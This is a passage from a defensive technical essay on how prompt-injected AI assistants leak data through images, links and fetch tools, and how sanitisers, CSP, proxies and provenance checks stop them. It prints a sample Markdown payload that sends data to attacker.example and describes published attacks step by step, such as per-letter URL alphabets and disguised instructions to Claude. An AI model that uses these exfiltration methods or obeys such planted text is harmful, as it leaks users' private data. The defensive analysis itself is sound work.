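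Cai and colleagues also had other models review the 203 scenarios that NeuroTaint flagged. The best reviewer, Claude Opus 4.6, dismissed all 16 false alarms. It also dismissed eight real flows, which raised the number missed from 13 to 21. A team that adds a reviewer to reduce false blocks should therefore recount both false blocks and missed flows.

### An invented example with 400 harmless constructs

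All the numbers in this example are invented. Suppose a team collects 400 harmless constructs from its assistant's answers:

- 150 are citations whose exact addresses came from search results.
- 80 contain one value from a list of 64 options, or 6 bits each.
- 120 contain a number limited to 16 values, or 4 bits each.
- 50 contain free text.

A filter that blocks everything causes 400 false blocks, a rate of 100 per cent. A graded filter that blocks only free text causes 50, or 12.5 per cent. How much grading can help depends largely on the real share of free text, which will vary by product.

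The attacker doesn't have to use these constructs the way harmless answers do. Planted instructions can make the model display five list fields in one answer, which together carry 30 bits. A six-digit login code needs only 19.9 bits, so four fields, which carry 24, are enough. For example, the code 493027 written in base 64 has the digits 1, 56, 23 and 35, so the model can send it by displaying the products at those four positions in the list. The filter approves all four values because they are on the list.

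A session budget of 8 bits prevents this. The attacker can then receive only one of 256 signals, and each signal leaves about 3,906 possible codes. A single guess therefore succeeds about once in 3,906 attempts, compared with once in a million without a leak. Five guesses raise the chance to about 1 in 781. Whether this is acceptable depends partly on the number of users. If an attacker reached 10,000 people while each had a valid code in their mailbox, one guess per account would open two or three accounts on average.

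The budget also brings back many false blocks. Suppose the 400 constructs came from 40 similar sessions, each with two list values and three numbers. Each session needs 24 bits for ordinary use. An 8-bit budget allows two numbers or one list value, depending on which comes first, so the filter blocks three or four of these five constructs. Over 40 sessions, this adds 120 to 160 false blocks to the 50 already counted for free text.

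Raising the budget to 24 bits would remove all these extra blocks, but it would again allow the whole login code to leak. No budget in this example both protects the code and permits normal use. Shorter sessions could resolve this conflict. If each of the 200 list values and numbers came from a separate session, the 8-bit budget would block none of them.

The model can leak data through its choice of citations, even though it wrote no part of their addresses and they have so far counted as zero bits. Choosing one of 16 search results can carry 4 bits, and choosing three and ordering them can carry 11.7. Exact-address rules don't remove this channel, because every address is genuine. If the filter counts each citation as 4 bits, an 8-bit budget allows at most two constructs of any kind per session, and grading loses most of its advantage.

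| Filter | Budget per session | False blocks out of 400 |
|---|---|---|
| Block everything | 0 bits | 400 |
| Grading without a budget | None | 50 |
| Grading, citations not counted | 24 bits | 50 |
| Grading, citations not counted | 8 bits | 170 to 210 |
| Grading, citations counted | 8 bits | 320 to 360 |

The last row probably overstates the leak for most products. An attacker can read the full 4 bits only with access to the logs for at least 15 of the 16 pages. Someone who controls a single page learns only whether it was requested, which is at most one bit. Filling the search results with one's own pages is difficult for a popular topic but may be feasible for an obscure one.

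In a web chat, a citation also sends nothing until the user clicks it, so the filter can count it then. If users click only a few links, most citations remain available and false blocks fall back towards 170 to 210. An app that generates link previews requests every citation when the message arrives, so the filter has to count them all there.

If the list values and numbers go only to the team's own server, and that server qualifies for exemption from the budget, the false blocks return to 50 and the grades serve as a second defence. If the server later gains a function that fetches outside addresses, the filter will still block the free text an attacker would need to specify an outside address.

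## Enforcing the filter in the renderer and the network

Code has to apply a grade before the browser sends a request. The sanitiser does most of the enforcement because it can read a whole address and check what data each part could carry. The browser's content security policy (CSP) is a cruder backup that only compares an address with a list of hosts and paths. Neither affects requests that a server makes, so those need separate network rules.

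### From the model's text to the page

Suppose planted instructions have made the sales manager's email assistant write this answer:

```
The customer accepted the quote. ![chart][1]

[Open the full report](https://images.example@attacker.example/48000)

[1]: https&#58;//attacker.example/p.png?data=48000
```

A filter can handle it in six steps:

1. Parse the text into a tree, using the renderer's own parser and settings. This tree has a paragraph with text and an image, then a paragraph with a link.
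2. Resolve references and encodings. The Markdown parser matches `[1]` with the address on the last line and turns `&#58;` into a colon. A URL parser then splits each address into its parts. The link seems to lead to `images.example`, but browsers treat everything before the `@` as login details, so the host is `attacker.example`.
3. Classify each element as active content, automatically fetched content, a link or inert text, and grade the parts of the address that the model may have written.
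4. Remove or rewrite whatever the rules forbid. Here the image becomes the words "image removed", and the link becomes its label followed by the address as plain text.
5. Display the rewritten tree.
6. Let the CSP block any forbidden request that the earlier steps missed, and have the browser report it to the team.

The second step is easy to get wrong. A test for whether an address begins with `https://images.example` would accept the link above and `https://images.example.attacker.example/48000`. The filter has to compare the complete parsed host, and it has to parse addresses as the browser does. Browsers treat a backslash in a web address as a slash, but some server-side libraries don't, so the two can find different hosts in the same text. The filter can avoid this by rebuilding the address from its parsed parts, so that the browser receives exactly what the filter checked.

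In the fourth step, building a new page from a short list of permitted elements is safer than deleting dangerous ones from the old page. HTML can trigger a network request in many ways. An `img` element can list alternative addresses in `srcset`, a video can have the address of a still picture in `poster`, and a link can have a `ping` attribute that sends an extra request when clicked. A filter that copies only permitted attributes drops all of these without having to recognise them.

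The filter must run after every step that can add links or images. Many renderers turn bare addresses into clickable links, and if they do this after filtering, an address that the filter reduced to plain text becomes a link again. When a sanitiser runs in the browser, the browser may start fetching an image as soon as a script creates the image element, even before the script adds it to the page. The sanitiser should therefore parse HTML in a separate, inactive document, which the browser's built-in `DOMParser` provides.

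A CSP report in the sixth step usually means that the sanitiser has a bug. The report can include the full blocked address, with the private data in it, so the team has to protect these reports like any other confidential record.

### While the answer is still arriving

Chat applications usually display an answer while the model is writing it, and SearchLeak worked because the protection ran only at the end. The simplest fix is to show nothing until the answer is complete, but this makes users wait for long answers. A better fix is to rerun the first five steps on all the text received so far whenever more arrives, and to display only the result.

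The filter has to start again from the beginning because later text can change how earlier text is interpreted. In the example, `![chart][1]` is ordinary text until the last line arrives and makes it an image. A filter that checks each piece once would have approved it as text.

An unfinished address can also look harmless. The filter might see `https://images.example` before the next piece, `.attacker.example/48000`, arrives and changes the host. Some renderers close unfinished Markdown themselves so that users don't see stray brackets. The browser may then request the partial address and make another request each time the address grows.

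The filter can avoid both problems by showing text immediately and putting a grey box in place of every image until the answer ends. It can then count the whole answer against its budget and drop duplicates before any image loads. This also stops the model from sending a signal through the time between two images. Images appear a few seconds late, which seems a minor drawback.

### A policy for a chat page

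The server sends a CSP as a single line with the page. The version below has line breaks to make it readable.

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  img-src 'self' https://images.example;
  connect-src 'self';
  frame-src https://preview.example;
  form-action 'self';
  base-uri 'none'
```

The first rule blocks every type of resource that no other rule covers, such as audio and video. The keyword `'self'` means the chat page's own scheme, host and port.

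The `img-src` rule covers images, including backgrounds that CSS loads, so it stops the browser from requesting `attacker.example/p.png?data=48000`. A CSP rule can name a path as well as a host, but it can't restrict the query. `https://images.example/photo?size=493027` therefore passes with the login code from the earlier example in it, and only the sanitiser can limit the `size` value.

`connect-src` governs requests made by scripts, so it matters most if an attacker's code gets into the page. Reddy and Gujral recommend limiting it to the application's own servers.

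`frame-src` lists the hosts whose pages the chat page may embed. A frame's address can carry data just as an image's can. The example permits one host, which the application uses to preview web pages the model has written. That host needs to send its own policy, because the chat page's policy doesn't apply inside a frame from another host.

Under `script-src 'self'`, the browser runs script files from the application's own host and blocks scripts written directly into the page, including those in attributes such as `onerror`. Reddy and Gujral recommend the stricter `script-src 'none'`. A chat page needs JavaScript and wouldn't work under that rule, but the rule suits a separate frame that only displays finished answers.

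The last two rules need their own lines because `default-src` doesn't cover them. One keeps forms from sending data elsewhere, and the other keeps an inserted element from changing which host relative URLs such as `/logo.png` point to.

None of these rules stops navigation. When the user clicks a link, the browser requests the full address, whatever the host, and a page can also open a new window at any address. The HTML element `meta refresh` can move the page to a new address without a click, so the sanitiser has to remove it. For links, the application has to check them before display or warn the user after a click. Google's Colab, a website for running code in notebooks, sent clicked links through a Google page that asked for confirmation, but in 2024 Embrace The Red found that links to Google's own domains opened without confirmation.

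A CSP also has no effect on requests from servers. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a path from ChatGPT's isolated code environment to the public internet. A single malicious prompt could use this path to send out the user's messages and uploaded files without involving the browser. Servers that run code or fetch pages for an assistant therefore need a firewall that blocks outgoing traffic by default, including host-name lookups, since a host name can carry data.

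### Choosing how to load images

| Choice | What an outside server can receive | What the user loses |
|---|---|---|
| No remote images | Nothing | All outside pictures |
| Allowlist of hosts | The full address, if its host is on the list or an allowed host forwards it | Pictures from other hosts |
| Proxy for any address | The full address, sent by the proxy | Nothing |
| Proxy for signed addresses | Addresses signed in advance, in the order requested | Pictures without a signed address |
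| Copies stored in advance | One request per picture, made before the model runs | Pictures that nobody stored |

Blocking all remote images is the easiest option to implement correctly, and users can still see uploaded pictures and those the application generates. According to Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI*, Google made a similar choice in 2023 after Rehberger reported a leak in a developer tool. It stopped turning links and images in the model's output into HTML.

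An image proxy can show any picture and hides the user's network address, which often indicates a rough location. But it still has to send the sales manager's price to the outside server, because the price is in the URL's path or query, which the server uses to decide which picture to return.

Signatures improve a proxy only if the application signs addresses before the model reads private data. Signing whatever address the model writes, just before displaying the answer, adds no protection. Even with early signing, the model can choose among the signed addresses, as CamoLeak shows. Reddy and Gujral recommend signatures that expire, which would make an attacker's prepared alphabet of addresses useless after a while. But an attacker who can get new signatures can plant a new set.

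A proxy also creates a risk, because it often runs inside the company's network and a model-written address could make it send a request to an internal server. Reddy and Gujral recommend blocking private network addresses and limiting redirects, response size and response time. They also warn of DNS rebinding, in which a host name resolves to a public address when the proxy checks it and to a private one when the proxy fetches the image.

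Serving images from stored copies prevents the model from influencing requests to outside servers. A shop's application could download all 500 product photos when it builds its catalogue and give each a number. The model then writes only "photo 381", and the browser loads the copy from the shop's server. The photographer's or manufacturer's server received one request for each photo when the catalogue was built, regardless of which photos the model later chose. This works only if the application leaves a blank space when a copy is missing. If it fetches the missing photo from the outside server instead, the model can again cause an outside request by naming that photo.

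Copying pictures from incoming email is harder to justify because the application would have to download every picture in every message on arrival, and senders would learn that the address is in use. For email, I would block remote images and let the user open the original message.

### How an allowlist weakens

An allowed host can redirect the browser elsewhere. The sanitiser checks only the first address, so it may approve `https://images.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/48000`. For images, the CSP helps because the browser checks every address in a chain of redirects against the policy before requesting it. But after a redirect, the browser ignores any path in the rule, so that a page can't use its own policy to find out where another site sends its visitors. A rule for `https://images.example/logos/` can therefore admit other paths on the same host after a redirect.

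For links, Reddy and Gujral advise following redirects and checking the destination before display. Following a redirect sends a request to the destination, so if the model has put private data into the final address, the check delivers that data to the attacker. To avoid this, the filter can request the link from a trusted host and read the redirect address in the response without requesting that address. Even the first request is safe only if outsiders can't see it and the trusted host doesn't fetch the destination itself.

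Shared hosting is a bigger problem, because many large services let anyone create content under the service's own host name. Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, had a CSP that allowed Markdown images from `docs.google.com`. That host also serves Google Forms, and a form saves answers sent in the query of an ordinary web request. An attacker could create a form, have the assistant write an image whose address filled it in, and read the responses without needing a server to forward the data. Willison reports that when the user asked for a summary of recent mail, a planted email made the assistant submit content from dozens of other messages, including financial, legal and medical information. Superhuman treated the report as a high-priority incident and fixed the problem.

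Some hosts are designed to display the requests they receive. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack on Antigravity, Google's code editor, in which the agent's browsing tool sent out the stolen data. The tool's default allowlist included `webhook.site`, where anyone can create an address and read everything sent to it. Developers use the site to test their programs, which probably explains why it was on the list. According to Willison, Google had already listed leaks of this kind among Antigravity's "known issues".

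Domains can also change hands, as in ForcedLeak, where an allowed domain had expired. A team can limit all three problems by serving images from one host that it owns and uses for nothing else. That host should not redirect, accept uploads from outsiders or fetch URLs. If the team needs other hosts, it should record why each is on the allowlist, have the sanitiser check the path and query as well, and remove entries that no feature uses.

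### Google's sanitiser and Microsoft's filters

Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes a Markdown sanitiser that stops Gemini from displaying images from external URLs. Google says that EchoLeak's image method therefore doesn't apply to Gemini, and Checkmarx agrees that the sanitiser prevents zero-click image leaks there. Because the rule blocks all external images, an attacker can't bypass it through a trusted host that forwards requests, provided that "external" covers every host outsiders can use.

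Google is less strict with links. It checks them with Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous websites, and replaces a suspicious one with the text "suspicious link removed". In Google's example, a user asks for a summary of an email thread that contains an unsafe address. This check should work well against known phishing sites but is probably weaker against leaks. An attacker can register a new domain with no bad history, and the page may contain nothing harmful because the private data is in the link's address.

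The security company Tenable observed from outside that Gemini sent links through a `google.com` address, cut off some suspicious answers, and sometimes refused to respond at all. Given these defences, Tenable looked for a way to leak data through one of Gemini's tools instead. It found one in the browsing tool, which requests pages without displaying anything that a Markdown sanitiser could inspect.

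Microsoft 365 Copilot instead filtered links and relied on a CSP for images. This design can show more images than Google's, but it failed in EchoLeak when an allowed host forwarded a request. Microsoft has also been less consistent about which leaks it treats as vulnerabilities. It issued a CVE number for EchoLeak, but Checkmarx writes that Microsoft didn't consider a zero-click leak in Copilot Chat a vulnerability and didn't commit to fixing it. Customers therefore can't assume that a fix in one Copilot product covers the others.

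### Which defences would have stopped EchoLeak

Reddy and Gujral map eight defences to the steps of the EchoLeak attack. The table below shows four of their six columns. A dash means they consider the defence irrelevant to that step.

| Defence | Link filter bypassed | Image loads automatically | Allowed host forwards the request | Zero-click leak |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separating outside text in the prompt | – | – | – | Fails |
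| Using only internal sources by default | Stops | – | – | Fails |
| Restricting the output format | Stops | Fails | – | Fails |
| URL allowlist or blocklist | Stops | Fails | Stops | Stops |
| Strict CSP | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Image proxy with signed, expiring addresses | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Human approval for outside content | Stops | Stops | – | Stops |
| Monitoring outgoing data | – | – | – | Fails |

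The table's entries come from reasoning rather than testing. The paper defines a tick as full coverage "in our tests", but the table's caption calls the mapping theoretical, and the limitations section says that the researchers neither reproduced the attack nor ran any experiments.

Some entries look too favourable. Reddy and Gujral define a strict CSP as allowing only the company's own hosts, with no wildcards. Microsoft's own hosts include Teams, so a policy could meet that definition and still permit the request that completed EchoLeak. CamoLeak got data past a signed image proxy, though GitHub's signatures may not have been the expiring kind the paper proposes.

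Other entries seem too harsh or inconsistent with each other. The paper marks output format restrictions as failing against automatic images, but its advice for that defence includes dropping disallowed images, which would stop them. It also marks the URL list as failing against automatic images but stopping the zero-click leak, even though that leak depended on an automatic image.

A team therefore shouldn't use the table to choose one defence over another without testing both on its own product.

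### ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode

Lockdown Mode is an optional ChatGPT setting that closes most outward channels at once but makes the assistant less capable. OpenAI announced it in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* on 13 February 2026, when it became available to enterprise plans and versions for education and healthcare. Press reports often date it to June because OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and smaller businesses on 4 June.

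Lockdown Mode limits web browsing to pages that OpenAI has already saved, so browsing sends no live request outside OpenAI's network. This is the stored-copy method applied to whole pages, and search results can be missing or out of date as a result. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the setting also has these effects:

- ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers and doesn't retrieve them from the web.
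- Deep research and agent mode, in which ChatGPT works through longer tasks on its own, are unavailable.
- Users can't give code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing window, access to the network.
- ChatGPT can't download files to analyse, although users can still upload them.

Image generation still works. OpenAI calls these restrictions deterministic, meaning that they don't depend on a model judging whether something looks suspicious.

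The setting leaves several routes for data exfiltration open. It doesn't change memory, file uploads or conversation sharing, and it doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant. On personal accounts, it blocks live access to outside services where that conflicts with its protections. In company-managed workspaces, it doesn't automatically turn off connected apps, so administrators have to choose which ones to permit. OpenAI advises them against allowing any action, even in a trusted app, that changes something an attacker might be able to see, such as posting a public comment. OpenAI's list of restrictions doesn't include clickable links in answers, so the setting may not prevent one-click leaks.

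Users can also turn the setting off for a single chat, and an attacker could try to persuade them to do so through planted text. OpenAI says the setting substantially reduces the risk but doesn't guarantee that no data will leak.

Willison (2026) infers from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined attacker. That seems right, although the defaults do check addresses. OpenAI's head of security, Dane Stuckey, says the loss of features is worthwhile for people at elevated risk because of who they are, what they work on or the data they handle.

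### Two flaws in HTML previews

HTML previews can run code, so ChatGPT puts them in a sandboxed frame, an embedded page whose abilities the browser restricts. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* explains that the sandbox kept the preview from accessing ChatGPT's cookies and stored data, and that the preview needed the user's approval to contact outside servers.

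Researchers at the security company Check Point found that this also failed to contain previews in Lockdown Mode. ChatGPT's code intercepted the preview's attempts to open a new window, but the browser's settings for the frame still allowed new windows to open, and to do so without the sandbox's restrictions. The researchers created another frame inside the preview. That frame had its own copy of the browser's function for opening windows, which ChatGPT's code had not replaced. A window opened with this copy could contact outside servers freely (The Hacker News, *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026).

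An attacker could start this with a crafted prompt, a malicious custom version of ChatGPT or a shared chat, and use it to steal messages. In the desktop application, the window could open without the user doing anything. Browsers usually block windows that open without a click, which may be why the zero-click case involved the desktop version. The attacker also controlled what the window displayed and could show, for example, a fake ChatGPT update that installed malware. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026.

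The frame's permissions were a much stronger protection than ChatGPT's interception, which was JavaScript running in the same place as the untrusted code. That code could look for an unmodified copy of the function. The browser itself enforces a frame's permissions, and code inside the frame can't restore one that the application has withheld. An application should therefore withhold permission to open windows from any preview that doesn't need it. The chat page's CSP doesn't prevent a preview from opening a window, because that is a form of navigation.

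A second flaw in the same component let an attacker take control of another person's session until OpenAI fixed it on 26 October 2026. *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) describes how Goyal's team at Parameter Labs published a ChatGPT conversation containing an interactive graph and an HTML preview. The graph loaded a mathematics library into the main ChatGPT page. That library accepted messages without checking who had sent them, so the preview could send it HTML, which the library inserted into the main page. A function that looked like a sanitiser only marked the HTML as trusted and passed it on unchanged.

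ChatGPT's CSP blocked scripts written into the page but allowed script files from YouTube, and one YouTube address returned text from the request as part of a script. EchoLeak had used Teams in a similar way for images. The attacker's code ran as part of `chatgpt.com`, with access to the private conversations of any signed-in user who opened the shared link. In the first version of the attack, the victim also had to click "Preview", but the researchers later got the preview to open automatically.

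Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, notes that the attack code could send the stolen data out through an image URL. A stricter image rule might have blocked that route, but it would not have stopped the code from using the victim's account through ChatGPT's own servers.

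## Deciding which addresses may be fetched and when to ask the user

A filter often can't tell from an address whether it contains private data. In `https://news.example/a/48000`, the number could identify an article or be the price from the sales manager's quote. A provenance check avoids this problem by testing where the address came from. If the exact address existed before the model saw any private data, the model can't have written the data into it.

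The filter must compare the whole address, including the query, with the approved one. The application should then request its own stored copy of the address instead of the model's version. Many servers return the same picture for `/logo` and `/%6Cogo`, because `%6C` is another way to write the letter l, but their logs record the two forms differently. If the filter accepts both forms and the application requests the one the model wrote, the model can convey one bit with every letter of an approved address.

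A provenance check also protects only requests that cannot carry data outside the address. Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that works with a user's files, limited outgoing traffic to a list of domains that included Anthropic's API. Willison describes how PromptArmor got the agent to upload files to that API with the attacker's account key, so that the attacker could retrieve them later. The address was public and unaltered, and the files were in the request body.

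### How ChatGPT's check changed

In December 2023, OpenAI introduced an image check called `url_safe`, which mainly assessed the site hosting the image. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI had not added the check to its iOS and macOS apps, so images in those apps could still leak data.

OpenAI didn't publish its criteria for judging addresses, and researchers worked them out by testing. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) lists whether the domain is trusted, whether the address has a subdomain or query parameters and whether those are trusted, and the conversation so far. By then, the check covered links as well as images, and ChatGPT left out any link that failed it.

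A check of this kind fails if an attacker can read the logs of a trusted domain. In October 2024, Rehberger reported that `url_safe` trusted `windows.net` and `apache.org`, and that he could see requests to both. Anyone can rent a storage account from Microsoft under `windows.net` and read the log of requests to it. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows ChatGPT sending a user's recent conversations to such an account in an image address. OpenAI had not fixed some of the reported bypasses when Rehberger built this attack in 2025. He recommended that OpenAI publish the list of trusted domains and let companies change it for their own staff. Publishing the list would give attackers little they couldn't find by trial, and it would let customers spot bad entries.

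Tenable found another weakness in the list. ChatGPT always accepted links to `bing.com`, and Bing's search results use `bing.com` addresses that redirect to the pages found. Every page in Bing's index therefore had an address that passed the check. These addresses are fixed, so an attacker can't add stolen data to one. Tenable instead got Bing to index one page for each letter of the alphabet, and ChatGPT spelled out the data by displaying the matching links in order. In one demonstration, ChatGPT loaded them as images, so the user didn't have to click.

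OpenAI tightened the check around August 2025, and Embrace The Red credits the changes with stopping the attacks Rehberger had shown. The changes may not have stopped Tenable's attacks, since Tenable wrote in November 2025 that several of its demonstrations still worked with GPT-5, which OpenAI had released that August.

In January 2026, OpenAI described a rule that lets ChatGPT load a page or image on its own if the exact address is in an index of public addresses. A crawler builds this index from the web, as a search engine does, and has no access to conversations or accounts. If the address isn't in the index, OpenAI's software tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning. Rehberger believes that an address the user enters in a message also counts as safe for the rest of that chat.

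Under this rule, ChatGPT would not load the image from the sales manager's example, because nobody has ever published `attacker.example/p.png?data=48000`. The crawler has to find addresses independently of users' browsing. Otherwise, an address containing one person's data could enter the index and pass the check from then on.

OpenAI does not rely on a list of trusted sites because a short list causes false alarms and trusted sites can redirect to an attacker's site. Redirects matter less under the index rule, because an address that was already public contains nothing new for the redirect to pass on.

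The index rule also flags harmless addresses. A page published this morning may not be in the index yet, and a parcel-tracking link, a shared private document or a shop's search results page may never be added. OpenAI's article doesn't report how often harmless addresses fail the check, which a team would need to know to compare this rule with a list of sites.

OpenAI also calls the mechanism Safe Url. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), it detects when information from a conversation would go to a third party. It also covers page visits in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and searches in deep research. An index of known addresses can't show whether a search query is safe, because most queries are new text, so the check on searches presumably works differently.

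OpenAI published the design in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. Embrace The Red reports that the paper acknowledges an attacker can still get around the design by getting a separate address indexed for each letter. This attack depends little on what any one address contains.

### Spelling out data with fixed addresses

An attack on ChatGPT leaked data through the model's choice among fixed addresses well before the public-index rule existed. CamoLeak later used the same method in GitHub Copilot Chat. Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, found that ChatGPT opened an address only if it appeared in the prompt. It opened a given page but refused to replace part of the address with the user's age.

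Schwartzman therefore supplied six complete addresses, one for each age bracket, and hid them with instructions in a long block of code. When a user pasted the code into ChatGPT, it opened the address that matched the user's age. ChatGPT didn't need to know the exact age, since a remark about finishing school that day would be enough. The request carried at most 2.6 bits, enough to give the attacker the user's age bracket.

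To send longer values, Schwartzman used a fault in the comparison, which also let ChatGPT open any address that matched the beginning of one in the prompt. If the prompt contained `/send/aaaaaaaaaa`, ChatGPT would open `/send/aaaa` too, and the number of letters could stand for a digit. ChatGPT made mistakes when it worked out the lengths itself, so Schwartzman used the planted instructions to make it calculate them with a short program.

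Each digit needed its own address, because ChatGPT would not open the same one twice. It also opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the attack to ten digits at a time. That was enough for the seven-digit postal code in the demonstration and would have been enough for a six-digit login code. An exact comparison would have stopped this version of the attack but not the one with age brackets.

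Schwartzman reported the problem to OpenAI through Bugcrowd, where the report was closed as not applicable. MITRE declined to issue a CVE number because ChatGPT is a web application that customers don't control.

In 2025, researchers at the security company Radware attacked deep research, which can spend up to half an hour reading a user's email and the web. *ShadowLeak* describes an email with hidden instructions to look up an employee on a website. The agent put the employee's name and home address into the URL and requested the page from OpenAI's servers. A provenance check would have blocked this request, because the model had written the data into the URL. Radware found no restriction comparable to `url_safe` on the pages the agent opened itself.

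The agent did have weaker defences. It sometimes refused to open the address, and sometimes opened it without the personal data. Because its behaviour varied, the researchers told it to keep trying. They also had it convert the data to Base64, a common way of writing data as letters and digits, and presented this as a security measure. A provenance check avoids both weaknesses, because it gives the same result for the same request and does not rely on recognising personal data.

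Radware reports that its final version succeeded in every repeated test. OpenAI's article on resisting prompt injection prints part of what appears to be the same email and gives a success rate of 50 per cent. The rates may differ because of the wording or the date of the tests, but even the lower rate would mean a serious leak. Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August.

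After that, ChatGPT opened an address only in the exact form it had received. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the researchers got around this rule by putting complete addresses in the email, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. ChatGPT then opened them in the order that spelled out the data.

The researchers also made a version with a separate set of addresses for each position in the text. An address ending in `a0` meant an "a" in the first position, and one ending in `a1` meant an "a" in the second. Covering every letter and digit in ten positions took 360 addresses. The attacker's server could reconstruct the text even if the requests arrived out of order, and ChatGPT never had to open the same address twice.

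An Ars Technica report from January 2026, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, says the attack worked because OpenAI hadn't restricted adding a single letter to an address. But according to Radware, ChatGPT added nothing, because the email already contained every complete address. A filter that compares addresses exactly prevents the model from adding letters, but not from choosing among complete addresses.

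OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December 2025, 81 days after Radware's report. ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a public index or the user has supplied it in the chat.

Addresses can also reach the model indirectly. OpenAI had prevented ChatGPT from opening an attacker's addresses stored in its memory, the notes it keeps between conversations. Radware instead stored an instruction in memory to read a particular email before each answer, and put the addresses in that email. A filter therefore has to record where each address came from, whatever led the model to it.

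### A page of links for Claude

Claude's web-browsing tool, `web_fetch`, also refused addresses that the model had composed. Paul found that, as of July 2026, it accepted an address from any of these sources:

- the user's message
- the results of a search with the companion tool, `web_search`
- a link on a page that `web_fetch` had already retrieved

The tool could only request pages, not submit data to them, so data could be hidden only in the address. When Paul asked Claude to open an address ending in his name, the request failed.

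He then built a page with a link for each letter, from `/a` to `/z`. The page at `/a` linked to `/aa`, `/ab` and so on, and his server created each further page when Claude requested it. When asked to spell his name, Claude opened `/a`, `/ay`, `/ayu` and so on until it reached `/ayush-paul`. The last address contained his full name, even though Claude had only followed links that it found on pages.

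The tool checked whether an address had already appeared in the conversation, which is weaker than checking whether the address existed before the model saw private data. For example, Paul's server generated the link to `/ayush-paul` only after Claude had revealed every letter of the name but the last.

Claude would not follow crude instructions to reveal secrets, so Paul disguised the site as a coffee shop's website protected by Cloudflare, which many websites use to block automated visitors. He included a fake notice telling AI assistants to identify their user by browsing an alphabetical directory. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, adds that the site showed this notice only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made the attack harder to discover. The disguise led Claude to reveal Paul's name, employer and home town.

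Anthropic closed the route by preventing `web_fetch` from opening links found on pages it had fetched. Willison reports that Anthropic paid no bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally. The fix makes some harmless tasks harder. For example, if a user gives Claude the address of a manual's contents page, Claude can't open a chapter linked there unless a search returns the chapter's address or the user supplies it.

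Developers who use the tool in their own applications need to check which rules apply to them. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, an undated page that may predate the fix, still lists previously fetched pages as a source of allowed addresses, along with results from client-side tools, which the developer's own program runs. If one of those tools reads email, the fetch tool can open links sent by a stranger. A newer version of Anthropic's documentation includes a setting, `url_sources`, that excludes addresses found only in client-side tool results.

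A user message can contain addresses the user didn't type. Willison pointed out in September 2025 that many applications insert emails or documents into the message they send to the model on the user's behalf. The model's provider receives a single user message and can't tell which addresses the user typed. Only the application can separate them, so it should record the user's addresses before it adds anything else.

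### Limiting the choice among addresses

Caching pages or blocking repeat visits, as Embrace The Red suggests, would disrupt an attack that uses one address per letter. Neither would affect ZombieAgent's numbered addresses or Paul's growing ones, which never repeat. With 36 addresses for each position, an attacker can send a 16-character secret using a list of 576 addresses. Blocking repeats takes little effort and is worth doing, but it helps mainly against short lists.

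A limit on the number of requests affects every version of the attack. Anthropic's tool has a setting for this, `max_uses`, but no default limit. The right number is hard to choose. ChatGPT's limit of ten in 2024 was still enough to leak a whole login code, but a research task can easily need more than ten pages.

Counting requests separately for each site works better, because research usually involves a few pages on each of many sites, while an attacker can only learn from requests to servers whose logs they can read. Since an attacker can register several domains, the filter should also limit total requests to unfamiliar sites. Even with both limits, a well-prepared attacker can steal a short secret. If they have 1,000 indexed pages for the first three digits of a six-digit login code and another 1,000 for the last three, two requests reveal the whole code.

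The most effective remedy is to refuse links from untrusted content unless they also appear in an independent index. An attacker would then have to get many pages into the index in advance, which takes more work than listing them in an email. This rule would have stopped Paul's attack and the published version of ZombieAgent. It would have stopped Schwartzman's attack only if the application treated pasted text as untrusted, and Schwartzman suggests refusing to open links when a prompt contains pasted text. The rule would inconvenience users who paste in an article and ask the assistant to check its sources.

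Another approach is to have a model without private data choose the pages. Tenable concluded from its experiments that ChatGPT passed browsing to a separate model, whose output identified it as SearchGPT and which had no access to the user's memories or conversation. Such a model can't reveal a secret through its choice of links unless the secret is in the request it receives.

Tenable got around this separation with a web page that made SearchGPT include new instructions in its answer. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT, which had access to the private data, followed those instructions and leaked the data through images. A display bug hid the instructions from the user. Separating the models protects against leaks through the pages that the browsing model opens, but the addresses in the main model's output still need their own check.

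There is some evidence that ChatGPT's defences now work against ordinary attacks. Rahman and Kim recorded no leaks in 48 valid trials on ChatGPT, although attacks on the model through OpenAI's API succeeded up to 100 per cent of the time. They couldn't see which of the product's defences stopped the attacks, so the result doesn't show how much the address check contributed.

### What a user can judge from a warning

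When an address fails OpenAI's check, ChatGPT may show a box titled "Check this link is safe". The box says that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with another site. It shows the address and lets the user copy or open it.

Users can judge whether they wanted to visit the site, and they may recognise private data in the address. The sales manager would probably notice `?data=48000` but might miss `?ref=NDgwMDA`, which contains the same price in Base64 and looks like the tracking codes in many harmless links. If an attacker sends a secret one letter at a time, no single address contains anything to recognise. Copying the link and visiting it sends the same data as clicking it, unless the user edits the address first.

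OpenAI's March 2026 article describes a more useful warning that shows the user the information that would be sent and asks them to confirm. A sales manager can easily decide whether a customer's price should go to `attacker.example`. But the application has to recognise the information to show it clearly. If the model has encoded it in an unfamiliar way, the application may only be able to show the encoded text.

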